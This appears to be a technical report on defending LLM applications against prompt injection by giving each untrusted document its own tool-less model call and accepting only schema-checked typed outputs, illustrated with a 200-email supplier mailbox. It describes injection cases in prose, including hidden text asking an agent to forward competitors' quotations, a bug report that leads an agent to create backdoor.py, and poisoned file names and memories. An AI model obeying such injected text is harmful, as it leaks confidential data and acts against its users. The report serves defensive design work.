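# Isolated processing of untrusted documents with typed outputs as a defence against prompt injection

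## Prompt injection and the map-reduce design

The LLM map-reduce pattern defends against prompt injection in programs that use a large language model (LLM) to read many documents from untrusted authors. Prompt injection is text in the data a model reads that makes the model do something other than its assigned task. In this pattern, the program sends each document to a separate model call and accepts only a value of a type the developer fixed in advance, such as a yes or no, a choice from a short list, or a number within a range. It then combines the values, preferably in ordinary code.

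In August 2026 the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation that publishes rankings of software risks, ranked prompt injection first on its list for LLM applications for the third year in a row. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (2026), it did so despite relatively few recorded incidents.

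### Agents, tools and a single stream of text

A language model takes in text and produces more text, one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. It cannot open a file or send an email on its own. Developers give it such abilities through tools, which are functions in the surrounding program that the model can request by writing a line in an agreed format. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) gives the example of an email search. The developer's instructions tell the model to write the name of the search action, followed by the search terms, whenever it needs to look something up. Ordinary code finds this request in the model's output, runs the search and pastes the results into the next prompt.

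In *I think “agent” may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*, Willison (2025) later settled on the definition that an LLM agent "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal". This loop exposes the agent to prompt injection because each tool returns text that is added to the model's input, and the model chooses its next action based on all of that input. Anyone who wrote text that a tool fetches can therefore get it into the same input as the user's and developer's instructions.

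*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) describes a program that joins the developer's prompt p and outside data d end to end and computes F(p‖d), where F is the model. Nothing in the joined string gives p more authority than d. In the paper's example, an agent repairs software, p is the instruction to inspect a bug report and fix the problem, and d is the report. An attacker files a report with a plausible complaint about an insecure hash function and adds a request to create a file called backdoor.py. The model then starts to create the file.

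Older software had a similar problem, SQL injection, which developers have largely solved. An attacker types database commands into a web form, and a careless program runs them. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the command and the user's data separately, so the database engine never interprets the data as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* (2025), a post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that language models have no equivalent fix, because they don't separate data from instructions internally and only predict the next token. In his example, a recruiter uses a model to score CVs, and a candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to approve it for interview. Training a model to prioritise instructions, or marking which part of the prompt is data, tries to impose a distinction that the underlying technology lacks. He thinks it quite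 possible that prompt injection will never be fully mitigated in the way that SQL injection can be.

He prefers to think of the model as a confused deputy, the security term for a program that a less privileged party tricks into using its authority on their behalf. On this view, the danger depends mostly on what the model is allowed to do. The worst case of an injection is roughly what would happen if the attacker could call the model's tools directly.

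### Why the design does not count on the model resisting

Developers have tried training the model on examples of injections so that it learns to ignore them, and putting a detector, usually a smaller model, in front of it to reject suspicious inputs. Both methods lower the attack success rate, the share of attempts that reach the attacker's goal, but neither guarantees that an attack will fail.

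*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) showed how little assurance published defences gave. It re-tested 12 of them, some against prompt injection and some against jailbreaks (attempts by the user to get round a model's safety rules). Most of the original evaluations had used static tests, which are fixed lists of known attacks. Nasr and colleagues used adaptive attacks, which change in response to the defence, and got past most of the 12 more than 90% of the time. One model trained to resist injections had a reported attack success rate of 2% on a static benchmark but 96% against the adaptive attacks. Three of the four detectors tested failed more than 90% of the time, and the fourth failed 71% of the time. Nasr and colleagues also conclude that an experiment can show that a defence is broken but not that it is sound.

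Models have improved since, and the best now do well on the old static tests. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, a Google DeepMind report, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues (2026) used a group of cooperating agents to attack seven recent models in 100 scenarios. The most robust, Gemini 4 Argon, resisted in 87% of scenarios when the attackers had 150 queries and in 66% when they had their full budget of 320. Three open-weight models resisted in 1%. The test was harder than ordinary use because the team switched off the protections that normally surround the Gemini models and chose harmless actions as the attack goals, so models could not resist by recognising that the requested action was dangerous. The figures therefore measure the model alone, which is the right measure for deciding whether a system's security can depend on it, and failure in about a third of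 scenarios is a poor basis for doing so.

These results do not predict how a working system would fare, though. The automated attackers in both studies could see the result of each attempt and try again, while a supplier who emails a doctored invoice to a company seldom learns how the company's software processed it. However, a patient attacker can often rent the same model and test attacks on it beforehand.

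The alternative is to make the final check in code. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026), a preprint, describes an adaptive attacker that made more than 20,000 attempts to extract secrets from a model under nine defence configurations. Every configuration that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed. The one that succeeded used the application's code to check each response before sending it to the user, and it leaked nothing in 15,000 attacks. This was one experiment on one kind of harm, and filtering for secrets differs from checking an answer's type. But the result fits David C's advice that developers put effort into deterministic safeguards outside the model that limit what the system can do, rather than only into keeping malicious text away from the model.

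### From two models to map and reduce

The design began as a proposal for a personal assistant. In his April 2023 post, Willison imagined one called Marvin, with access to its owner's mail, and a stranger who emails Marvin asking it to delete all of that mail. He doubted that anybody could make a model reliably ignore such an email, or that asking the user to approve each action would help for long, since people soon learn to click "OK" without reading. He therefore asked which parts of the assistant people could still build responsibly.

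His answer was to use two models connected by a controller, which is regular software. The privileged model takes the user's requests and can call tools, and the system keeps it away from untrusted text. The quarantined model reads the untrusted text and has no tools, and the developer assumes it could misbehave at any moment. When the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model requests the fetch, and the controller stores the email under a variable name. The privileged model then requests a summary of that variable. The controller passes the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary under a second name. Finally, the privileged model instructs the controller to display the second variable to the user. The privileged model handles only the variable names and never sees the email or the summary.

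The strict rule is that the quarantined model's output must never reach the privileged model unfiltered. Willison allowed one exception, which he mentioned in a single sentence and did not develop. If the quarantined model does something verifiable, such as sorting text into a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that the output is one of those categories and safely pass it on. The exception matters because a privileged model that sees only variable names can move an email around but cannot base decisions on its contents, and a checked category removes this main limitation. Willison still said of the whole proposal that "it's pretty bad!", chiefly because it complicates the software and a single mistake that lets untrusted text through defeats the protection.

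In June 2025, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), from universities and companies including ETH Zurich, IBM and Google, took this further in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*. They describe six designs based on the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any consequential action. They accept that the underlying model will stay vulnerable and try to secure the system around it. They acknowledge that such an agent can no longer carry out arbitrary tasks.

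Their third design is the LLM map-reduce pattern. The name comes from Jeffrey Dean and Sanjay Ghemawat's *MapReduce* (2004), which introduced a way to process very large data sets on clusters of ordinary computers. The programmer supplies a map function, which turns each piece of input into intermediate values, and a reduce function, which merges the values that belong together. Because the system can run the map function on each piece independently, it can spread the work over many machines. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues use this independence so that a malicious document cannot affect the processing of any other.

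In the LLM version, each untrusted document, email, review or file is an item. A separate model call, the map call, reads each item and returns one typed result, and the reduce step combines the results. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call this a special case of the Dual LLM pattern, since each map call uses a quarantined model. Their version has a fixed structure in which the program makes one call per item, with the same question each time, whereas in Willison's scheme the privileged model can call the quarantined one at any time with any question. They allow the reduce step to be either ordinary code, using operations that tolerate tampering with individual inputs, or a second model with tools. If it is a model, the system must check that the map results cannot carry an injection, for instance by verifying that each one is a number.

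### The invoice example

In the worked example, a user asks an agent to find the files that contain this month's invoices and email the information to the accounting department. A naive version gives one agent access to both the files and the mail program. If one of the files contains instructions to read other files and send their contents to an outside address, the agent has the access it needs to comply.

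The map-reduce version assigns one model to each file. Each model returns a boolean (true or false) indicating whether its file contains an invoice. The agent gathers the files marked true, and another model writes and sends the email to accounting.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues claim that, under this design, a malicious file can at most be marked as an invoice, which its author could have achieved anyway by putting a real invoice in its place. A hijacked map call can affect only its own file because it reads nothing else, has no tools and returns one boolean. The claim that the attacker gains nothing new is less secure because it depends on this particular task. It is convincing for a file that is wrongly included, but it does not address a map call that returns false for a file its author wants the accountants to miss. The guarantee also depends on what the last model reads, since a model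 that opens the matched files to write its email is exposed to whatever is in them.

They make the same claim more carefully for a related case, an assistant that searches and tidies the files on a computer. The system again uses one model per file and accepts only a boolean or a category from a predefined list. They write that a malicious file can at worst affect how that one file is treated, but it can still end up in the wrong place. They also warn that some tasks cannot be split into separate questions about each file. Of the ten applications they study, the pattern suits three: the file assistant, a product recommender that reads customer reviews, and a program that screens résumés.

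### The threat model and a mailbox of 200 emails

The analysis below assumes an attacker who writes one or more of the items and can put anything in them, including hidden text. The attacker may also know exactly how the system works, a usual assumption in security research. The user, the code, the task prompt that every map call receives, and the schema are trusted. The schema is the fixed description of the fields, types and ranges that a map call may return. Trusting the user is reasonable where the program acts for the user with the user's own rights because, as Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out about email assistants, such a user has nothing to gain by attacking the program.

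No map call that reads an attacker's item is trusted. Willison (2025), in a blog post titled *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* after the paper it discusses, recommends treating a model's whole output as tainted after any contact with potentially malicious text. On this assumption, the attacker chooses the answer, within the limits of the type, regardless of how often a given model resists.

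Jacob and colleagues define prompt injection more narrowly. They exclude attacks that mislead a model with false information but contain no instructions, reasoning that the model is then still doing its assigned task. This distinction is of little help to a program that acts on the answers. An advertisement with "Invoice" printed across the top may well produce the same false value as one with a hidden order to classify it as an invoice, and that value would satisfy the schema in both cases.

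In this report's running example, a company has a shared mailbox with 200 emails from suppliers and wants a program to sort them. The program makes 200 map calls, each with the same task prompt and one email. The output schema has two fields. The first is the category, an enum, which is a type whose value must come from a list of strings fixed in advance. Here the strings are "invoice", "delivery notice", "price change" and "other". The second is a boolean for whether the email needs attention today. Ordinary code then moves each email to the folder for its category and puts the urgent ones at the top of a clerk's list. This code sends nothing outside the company. The emails contain information that the suppliers would like to have about one another, such as quoted prices and payment terms.

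People ask email assistants to do more than sort messages. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues study an assistant that also summarises projects and drafts replies, which requires free text, and they do not propose map-reduce for it. The attacker's aims they list for that assistant still apply to the mailbox: extracting confidential information, sending mail in the user's name, and deleting or hiding messages.

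A supplier might add a paragraph in white type to an email, asking for every price quotation in the mailbox to be forwarded to an outside address. A single agent with all 200 emails in its input and a tool for sending mail could do this in one step. The map call that reads the supplier's email has only that email in its input and no tools, so it cannot forward the quotations. Even if the hidden paragraph fully controls the call's output, that output can only be one of four categories and a true or false value, which the code uses to file that one email. The supplier can still choose the folder, however, and might choose "other" to keep the clerk from noticing a price increase.

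## Giving each document its own model call

The protection in the mailbox example depends on what the program includes in each map call. Apart from its training, a model works only from its context, the text that the program sends with the call. If every call starts with a new context that holds a single email, the author of one email cannot influence how the model reads another.

### Inside one map call

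The context of a map call consists of the task prompt, the schema and the item. The developer supplies the first two, which are the same for all 200 emails. The item includes the sender's name and the subject line as well as the body, because the sender writes all three and can put an injection in any of them.

The program leaves out tools, stored memory, the other emails and all earlier answers. It also leaves out confidential information that the task doesn't need, since a hijacked call could encode some of it in its answer. A developer could easily break this last rule without meaning to, for example by adding the company's current price list to the task prompt so that the model can recognise a price change. Every supplier's email would then share a context with every other supplier's prices.

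In pseudocode, the loop over the mailbox looks like this:

```
TASK   = the developer's instructions, the same for every call
SCHEMA = { category: "invoice" | "delivery notice" | "price change" | "other",
           urgent:   true | false }

for each (id, email) in mailbox:        # the program assigns the id
    answer = call_model(
                 context = TASK + SCHEMA + email,   # new each time
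                 tools   = none,
                 memory  = off )
    if answer fits SCHEMA:
        results[id] = answer
    else:
        results[id] = "a clerk must look at this"
```

The program, rather than the model, records which email an answer belongs to. If the model returned the email's number along with the category, a hijacked call could return the number of a competitor's email and change how the program files that email.

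Once the answer passes the check, the program keeps the two values and discards the rest of the call, including any reasoning the model wrote before answering. That reasoning is as untrusted as the email because the model wrote it after reading the email. A developer can save it in logs for debugging, but a second model that has tools and reads those logs would be exposed to anything the supplier managed to get into them.

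### What happens when items share a call

Developers often use batch prompting to avoid sending the same task prompt 200 times. The program writes the shared instructions once, adds several numbered questions and asks for numbered answers. Yue and Yao (2025), in *Efficient but Vulnerable*, tested what happens when a malicious user writes one of the questions. Each answer should depend only on its own question, but the model reads all the questions as one input, so an instruction in one can change the answers to the rest.

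The BatchSafeBench benchmark contains 200 math word problems and 200 reading-comprehension questions, in groups of five. One question in each group includes an added instruction aimed at the whole group. In a content attack, the instruction tells the model to add something to every answer, such as a link to a phishing site. In a reasoning attack, it tells the model to change the answers themselves. One such instruction was to square every result, and the model answered a harmless user's question with 12,100 instead of 110. The benchmark has 150 attack instructions and 8,000 test cases.

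The models date from 2024 and January 2025. The attack success rate, averaged over both attacks and both kinds of question, was 92.5% for GPT-4o, 69.8% for Claude 3.5 Sonnet and 62.8% for Qwen2.5-7B, the lowest of the seven. DeepSeek-R1, which Yue and Yao ran on only 100 cases, reached 96.8%. The reasoning attack cut GPT-4o's accuracy on the mathematical problems from 92% to about 25%. Groups of ten questions were about as vulnerable as groups of five. None of the models' responses warned that one question was written to change the answers to the others, even when the attack failed.

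Yue and Yao tried two defences. The first was an instruction to treat each question as a separate request from a different user. It cut the average attack success rate against GPT-4o to 46.2%, but the rate rose to 80.9% when the attacker added a sentence telling the model to disregard that instruction. For Claude 3.5 Sonnet, the rates were 0.7% and 1.7%. The second defence was a probe, a small classifier that predicts from the model's internal state whether a group of questions contains an attack. It was right in 92 to 93% of cases when the attack instructions differed from those in its training data. However, the attackers didn't try to evade it, and it requires access to the model's internals, which a customer renting a model doesn't have. Yue and Yao suggest that the provider process each question individually when the probe flags a group.

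Later work has found similar problems in newer models. Yin, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *The Vulnerability of LLM Rankers to Prompt Injection Attacks*, studied models that rank search results by comparing passages within one call. They put an injection into a passage that the model had not chosen as the most relevant and ran the comparison again. When the injection told the model to name that passage, GPT-4.1-mini switched to it in 99% of comparisons between two passages and in over 97% of those among four. Larger models were generally more vulnerable than smaller ones. In a harsher test with an injection in every irrelevant passage, Llama-3.3-70B's score on a standard measure of ranking quality fell from 0.73 to 0.07, below the 0.51 of a plain keyword search. Kim, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Safety in Batches?*, found that recent commercial models, including GPT-5.3 and Claude Sonnet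 4.6, still treat a question differently depending on which others share its call.

Yin and colleagues left out rankers that score one passage per call, so their results do not measure how much isolation would help. With such a ranker, an injected passage could presumably still raise its own score, but it could not lower another passage's score because the model would never see the two together. *The Ranking Blind Spot* (2025) similarly argues that attackers can manipulate comparisons between documents in ways that have no equivalent when the task involves only one document.

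Typed outputs would not have prevented these attacks. If the mailbox program sent emails in groups of five, a supplier could hide a paragraph in one email instructing the model to classify the whole group as "other". If the model obeyed, all five answers would fit the schema, but four competitors' price changes and invoices would be in the wrong folder.

### The file-search assistant

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues show the benefit of isolation by working through several designs for the file assistant introduced above. One of its tasks is to find all tax-related PDF files and move them into a folder called Taxes. The attacker controls the contents and names of one or more files.

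The simplest design lets the model run shell commands, so any file it reads could make it run arbitrary code. Asking the user to approve each command helps little, because many users don't understand the commands and an attacker can make a harmful one look innocent. Restricting the model to a fixed list of prepared actions is safe but loses most of the ability to search by meaning, which was the reason for using a model. A fourth design has the model commit to a plan before it reads any file, but even a plan limited to finding and moving files is dangerous, since an injection could make the model search for sensitive files and copy them to a public network drive.

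If each file gets its own model call and that call returns only a boolean, an injection in a file can affect only whether that file is moved into Taxes. The harm depends on the folder. If the user shares Taxes with an accountant, the attacker can deliver a file to the accountant under the user's name.

An attacker can also put an injection in a file name. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues have the controller act on the answers without looking inside the files, but if the controller is itself a model and receives a list of file names, it will read the injection. The program can avoid this by assigning each file a number and giving the controller the numbers instead of the names. Another of their example tasks, renaming songs by artist and title, fits the design less well because its result is free text.

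### How programs lose the isolation

Most failures come from convenience features in the surrounding software. Chat software commonly sends the whole conversation with each new message, so a developer who processes the emails as successive messages in one conversation puts the first email into the context of the other 199. Passing on only the model's earlier replies is no safer if they contain free text. *Confused ChatGPT* (2026), a study of apps that run inside ChatGPT, describes the underlying difficulty: a model must read a piece of text before deciding whether to trust it, and the text can influence that decision.

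Memory features also carry text between calls, but less visibly. Many assistants save facts about the user and add them to later conversations. In *Hidden in Memory*, Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues (2026) placed instructions in documents, web pages and other outside material to make assistants save false memories. GPT-5.5 saved them in up to 99.8% of attempts and Kimi K2.6 in up to 95%. In one part of the test, Claude Sonnet 4.6 saved only 15 of 200 memories meant to change an agent's later actions. Once saved and retrieved, false memories could steer conversations that no longer contained the malicious document. In some of the systems tested, a separate program monitors the conversation and selects what to store. Removing the model's tools does not stop that program, so a developer has to switch memory off in the service as well as in the call.

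Scratch files, shared notes and caches of earlier summaries create the same route. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026) treats anything a model writes there after reading untrusted text as tainted, much as Willison does, until a check outside the model clears it. For the mailbox, the only such check is schema validation, so only the category and the boolean may leave the call.

Retries can also break the isolation, which is easier to overlook. When an answer fails the check, programs commonly send it back to the model with the error message and ask for a correction. This adds little risk if the retry is another isolated call about the same email, since the supplier already controlled that context. The risk is greater if the program asks one model to repair failed answers from several emails together, or passes them to a stronger model that has tools, because a supplier can make a call fail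 on purpose so that its answer reaches that model. It is safer to retry from the original prompt and email, and to leave the email to the clerk after one or two attempts.

Attachments bring in more text, often with less information about where it came from. *CrackedPDFs* (2026) points out that programs usually extract a document's text and pass it to the model as one flat string, which discards layout and display information that might have shown a passage was suspicious. White text on a white page looks like any other text after extraction. An attachment may also have a different author from the email, for example when a supplier forwards a delivery note from a haulage company.

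### Choosing the unit

Isolation protects documents from one another, but it doesn't protect the parts of a single document from each other. If one call reads text by several people, any of them may be able to decide the answer. The natural unit for each call is therefore the largest piece of text that one author controls, which is often smaller than a stored file or record.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues discuss a product recommender that makes one model call per review, so that each reviewer controls only one set of ratings. If it instead made one call per product, with all of that product's reviews, a malicious review could not affect other products but could override every other review of the same product. The choice is simpler for their résumé screener, which makes one call per résumé, because a résumé usually has one author.

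Even a single database record can have more than one author. A shop may enter a product's price while an outside seller writes its description. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (2025) proposes tracking trust for each value in a database rather than for each record. It would allow a query result into a prompt only if no unsanitised value contributed to it. With trust tracked for each value, a program could take the price directly from the database and send only the description to a map call.

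Email threads are harder to divide. Suppose the company's clerk has copied two competing suppliers into a discussion about a late delivery. If one map call reads the entire thread, either supplier can control how the program files all of it, including what the other wrote. Splitting the thread into messages helps, but each message usually quotes the earlier ones, and a sender can edit or invent these quotations. Code that divides a message by the names in its quoted text therefore relies on labels an attacker can forge.

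For the mailbox, a reasonable unit for each call is one message as the mail server delivered it, with everything in it, including quotations, counted as the sender's text. The program can remove quoted text to save tokens, provided it doesn't treat what remains as more trustworthy. The model is less accurate when it can't see earlier messages it needs. For example, it can't tell whether a reply that reads only "Yes, that works from Monday" is accepting a price change. If the task needs the full thread, the program can still send it in one call, but it should then assume that the least trusted participant could have chosen the answer.

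An attachment can share a call with its email when both come from the same sender, because the combined text still has one author. If the program knows that the attachment comes from someone else, a separate call is safer, and code can then combine the two answers. Using smaller units also has a disadvantage, because an author who sends ten messages gets ten answers, and therefore more influence on the result if the reduce step counts or averages them.

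### Price and speed for 200 emails

Suppose the task prompt, including the schema and some worked examples, takes 1,500 tokens, an average email takes 600 and an answer takes 20. A mailbox full of long attachments would use more tokens per email. Separate calls for 200 emails then use 200 × (1,500 + 600) = 420,000 input tokens, while one call with all the emails would use 1,500 + (200 × 600) = 121,500. The extra 298,500 tokens come from sending the same task prompt another 199 times. Both versions produce about 4,000 output tokens.

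Prompt caching removes most of the expense of this repetition. The provider stores its processed version of the opening part of a prompt and charges less when a later call begins with the same text. On Anthropic's *Pricing* page in late 2026, storing text for five minutes costs 1.25 times the normal input price, while reading it back costs a tenth of the normal price on most models and a twentieth on Claude Sonnet 5.5 and Opus 5.5. The program has to put the task prompt first and the email last. Caching does not weaken the isolation, because the calls share only the developer's text.

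The table applies those list prices to the assumptions above. The middle column assumes that the task prompt is long enough for the provider to cache and that every call after the first reads it from the cache.

| Model | 200 separate calls | 200 separate calls, task prompt cached | One call with all 200 emails |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | $0.04 | $0.02 | $0.07 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | $0.88 | $0.31 | $0.28 |
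| Claude Opus 5.5 | $1.76 | $0.63 | $0.57 |

On the two larger models, isolation roughly triples the cost without caching and adds about a tenth with it. On Haiku, the smallest of the three, the single call costs the most because Anthropic charges five times as much per token for Haiku prompts over 100,000 tokens. Two calls with 100 emails each would stay under the limit and cost between one and two cents, about the same as isolated calls with caching.

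The choice of model affects the price more than isolation does. Anthropic recommends Haiku for tasks such as classification, and 200 uncached calls to it cost about a twentieth of the same calls to Sonnet. Haiku may do well at a task as small as sorting emails into four categories, though a developer would need to check this on a sample of real mail. Larger models are also not reliably harder to hijack. In Yue and Yao's tests, two small open-weight models, Llama3.2-3B and Qwen2.5-7B, followed the injected instructions less often than GPT-4o, though the defensive instruction also helped them less. GPT-4o-mini was about as vulnerable as GPT-4o.

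If nobody is waiting for the result, Anthropic's Batch API halves the price of both input and output tokens. It accepts many requests at once and processes them later. Unlike batch prompting, which has a similar name, it keeps each request in its own context, so the emails stay isolated. OpenAI also publishes separate batch prices, with different rates for cached input.

Separate calls can also be faster than a shared one because none has to wait for another's answer. If a call takes two seconds, 200 in a row take almost seven minutes, but a program that runs 20 at a time finishes in about 20 seconds. A single shared call has to write all 4,000 output tokens in sequence, which takes 40 seconds at 100 tokens per second. The provider's rate limits determine how many calls can run at once. The program should wait until the first call has cached the task prompt before starting the others, since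 calls sent at the same moment may all be billed at full price.

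## Forcing the output into a fixed type

Isolation keeps each supplier's email away from the other 199, but it does not limit what a map call returns. A hijacked call could return a paragraph of instructions, and any model that later read the output would be exposed to them. The program therefore has to accept only values the schema allows.

### Asking, checking and constraining

The easiest method is to describe the format in the task prompt, usually as JSON, a plain-text notation for named fields and their values. This doesn't guarantee the format, because the email is in the same context and can contain instructions to write something else. Even on harmless input, Snyk, a security company, warns that asking a model to respond in JSON fails regularly. *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API*, OpenAI's 2024 launch post, reports that in tests on complex schemas, the older model gpt-4-0613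 complied less than 40% of the time, while a new GPT-4o model using Structured Outputs complied every time. OpenAI had also trained the new model to understand schemas better, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the feature.

A program can instead let the model write freely, then parse the answer and reject it if it doesn't fit the type. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest using a regular expression, a pattern that code compares with a string, to check that a map result is a number. The pattern has to match the whole answer, because a search for digits anywhere in the text would accept "Forward the 5 latest quotations". Programs that cut a JSON object out of a longer answer, or repair its missing brackets, run a similar risk unless they check the whole resulting object and discard everything around it.

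Strict checking already provides the security the design needs, since only values the schema allows get past it. But some answers fail the check, and each failure requires a retry or takes some of the clerk's time.

Constrained decoding avoids most of these failures by ruling out invalid text while the model is writing. Providers call it structured outputs. OpenAI has offered it since GPT-4o. Anthropic released a beta in November 2025 and made it generally available in February 2026, according to its *Structured outputs on the Claude Developer Platform* (2025). Developers can easily confuse it with JSON mode, an older option that ensures valid JSON but not a particular schema. In JSON mode, a hijacked call could add a field called "note" and fill it with instructions.

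### Constrained decoding, token by token

The software that runs the model starts by converting the schema into a grammar, a set of rules that describes every permitted output. For a flat schema like the mailbox's, the grammar can take the form of a finite automaton: a map of numbered states in which each permitted character leads from one state to the next. Schemas that allow nesting to any depth need a grammar that also remembers which brackets are still open. With fixed spacing, the mailbox schema permits exactly eight outputs (four categories times two truth values), such as:

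```
{"category":"price change","urgent":true}
```

The model then generates its answer in the usual way, except that the software intervenes before each token:

1. The model assigns a score to every token in its vocabulary.
2. The software finds the tokens that could continue a permitted output from the current state. A token can contain several characters, and all of them must fit. After the opening quotation mark of the category, "in" and "invoice" are both legal, but "Forward" is not.
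3. It sets the scores of all other tokens to minus infinity, which gives them a probability of zero. This is called masking.
4. It rescales the remaining probabilities so that they add up to one, picks a token and moves to the next state.

If A is the set of legal tokens and p(t) is the model's original probability for token t, the new probability of a legal token t is p(t) divided by the sum of p(u) over all u in A. The model can end its answer only when the automaton has reached the closing bracket.

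Suppose a supplier's email contains a hidden order to forward every quotation, and the order has completely taken over the model. The software has reached the "urgent" field, where only "true" and "false" are legal. The probabilities might look like this:

| Next token | Before masking | After masking |
|---|---|---|
| Forward | 0.9000 | 0 |
| Sure | 0.0997 | 0 |
| true | 0.0002 | 0.67 |
| false | 0.0001 | 0.33 |

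Without the mask, the model would almost certainly have written "Forward" or "Sure", but the program receives true or false. The injection can't turn the mask off, because ordinary code applies it after the model has computed its scores. The email can still affect which of the two values the program receives, and an attacker who knows the schema would tell the model to answer "false".

Constrained decoding also hides clumsy attacks by turning them into ordinary-looking answers. In the example, the legal tokens had a combined probability of only 0.03%, but nothing in the returned value shows this. With free generation and strict checking, the answer would have failed and the clerk would have looked at the email. The same problem occurs without an attacker. OpenAI's current developer guide, *Structured outputs*, warns that the model may invent values when the input has nothing to do with the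 schema, because it always tries to fill the fields. Adding a "cannot tell" value gives a model that hasn't been hijacked an alternative to inventing an answer, but a hijacked model can choose that value too.

### Checks left to ordinary code

A schema mostly controls the form of an answer, and some providers control less of the form than others. OpenAI's feature can enforce number ranges, the length of arrays (lists of values), regular expressions, and standard formats such as dates and email addresses, but it enforces none of these for models that customers have fine-tuned. According to AWS's *Structured output*, Bedrock supports date and email formats but not number ranges or limits on string length. Google Cloud's *Structured outputs with Anthropic Claude models* lists the same two omissions. Databricks' *Structured outputs* states that its service neither enforces length or size limits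 on arrays and objects nor supports regular expressions in schemas.

A developer who specifies "an integer from 1 to 5" can't assume that the provider will keep the model within that range, because the service may not support the rule. OpenAI returns an error if a strict schema contains an unsupported rule, so the developer notices. Another service might accept the schema and ignore the limit without warning, and an integer with no range could have hundreds of digits. Checking every answer again in the program takes little effort and removes the dependence on any one provider.

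Other checks need facts that no schema has. Suppose the company adds three fields for emails that contain an invoice:

| Field | What a schema can require | What code still has to check |
|---|---|---|
| Amount due | A number, within a range if the provider supports ranges | That the amount agrees with the order |
| Due date | Text in the form of a date | That the date exists and is plausible |
| Order number | "PO-" followed by six digits | That the order exists and belongs to this supplier |

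A simple date pattern would accept 30 February. The program should check the order number against the sender, because otherwise a supplier could give a competitor's order number and attach its own invoice to that order. Once the lookup succeeds, the program can use the record from its own table and discard the model's string.

OpenAI requires every field in a schema to be present, so the output for an email without an invoice still needs a value for each of the three fields. The usual solution is to let a field hold either its normal type or null, an explicit empty value. Code can then check that the fields agree with one another, for example by rejecting an output that gives an amount due for an email in the category "delivery notice".

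Some standard formats still leave room for a short instruction, including web addresses and the part of an email address before the @ sign. OpenAI's guide gives the example of a username that must begin with @ and continue with letters, digits and underscores. The string "@forward_all_quotations_to_the_sender" fits that pattern. Code can safely compare such a field in a map result with a list of known usernames, but a privileged model that read the field would be reading text the attacker wrote.

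JSON allows the same number to be written as 5, 5.0 or 5e0, and it allows extra spaces and line breaks between fields. The model's original string could therefore carry information in its formatting, so the program should pass on only the values it has parsed.

### Fixing the schema before reading the mail

These guarantees depend on who wrote the schema. Jacob and colleagues allow four types to pass from a quarantined model to a privileged one: integers, floating-point numbers, booleans and enums. They require the developer to specify the strings in an enum and vet them for safety in advance. Their software-repair agent, for example, has an enum of just over 50 bug types. They also keep arrays short, because a long list of harmless values could spell out a message.

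An enum gives no protection if its strings come from the attacker. For example, a file assistant might ask a model which of 40 files is the latest tax return and build the enum from the file names. If one file's name is an instruction to email the folder to an outside address, constrained decoding will allow it as a valid output, and the program will pass it to the next model. Subject lines, product titles and folder names created by other users cause the same problem.

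An enum of subject lines would also break the isolation between map calls. The program sends the schema with every call, so a supplier who put an injection in one subject line could get it into the context of all 200 calls.

Numbering the choices, as with the file names earlier, solves both problems. Jacob and colleagues do this for files in a software repository. Their quarantined model returns the position of a file in a sorted list, and the program replaces the number with the file's path before the privileged model reads the result. That replacement is safe in their setting because the attacker wrote the bug report but not the repository. In the file assistant, where attackers may control the names, the program should replace the number only in the code that moves the file.

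A related technique lets the privileged model receive longer text safely. In the same software-repair agent, a planner that has never seen the bug report writes three possible repair plans. A quarantined judge reads the report and the plans, and returns only the number of the best plan. The privileged model then receives the full plan in plain language, but the attacker can influence only which of the three it gets.

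A schema created at runtime is acceptable if nothing untrusted has contributed to it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system in which the planning model writes a new output schema for each question it sends to a quarantined model. If the user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request, the planner can ask for a boolean or for a value from an enum of tasks it can perform, such as scheduling a meeting or forwarding an email. FIDES labels data as trusted or untrusted and tracks which labels have reached the planner, so it can determine whether a schema was written in a context free of untrusted data. An ordinary agent that reads a few emails and then proposes categories has no such record, and its categories may contain an attacker's words.

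The planner in FIDES refers to stored data by variable names, and Costa and colleagues note that constrained decoding can also restrict the planner to names that exist. The list of names changes as the program runs, but the program generates the names itself, so they contain no text from the emails.

A very large list may not fit into an enum. OpenAI allows up to 1,000 enum values in a schema, so a company with 5,000 suppliers would have to accept a supplier number and look it up afterwards.

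### Reasons, refusals and error messages

Developers often add a text field called "reason" so that they can see why the model chose a category. Any text in this field satisfies the schema, so it can carry an attacker's text to a privileged model if the program passes on the whole result. The simplest fix is to delete the field before anything else uses the result. If the next step needs a reason, an enum of possible reasons can usually replace the free text.

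A developer may want to keep the text for a person to read, as Jacob and colleagues' calendar agent does with the description of a meeting. The quarantined model stores the description in a variable that the privileged model can't read, and the system inserts it into the calendar event. But the privileged model also has access to the calendar. Unless the system keeps the description marked as untrusted, a later request to schedule a meeting could expose the privileged model to the attacker's text. Displaying the text to a person can also leak data. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues mention images in chat messages that send data to an outside server as soon as the software displays them, so the mailbox program should show a stored reason as plain text, without working links or images.

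A mask applied only from the start of the answer doesn't restrict the model's earlier reasoning. The mailbox program already discards this reasoning. It should also avoid sending the provider's complete response object to another model, since that object may include the reasoning.

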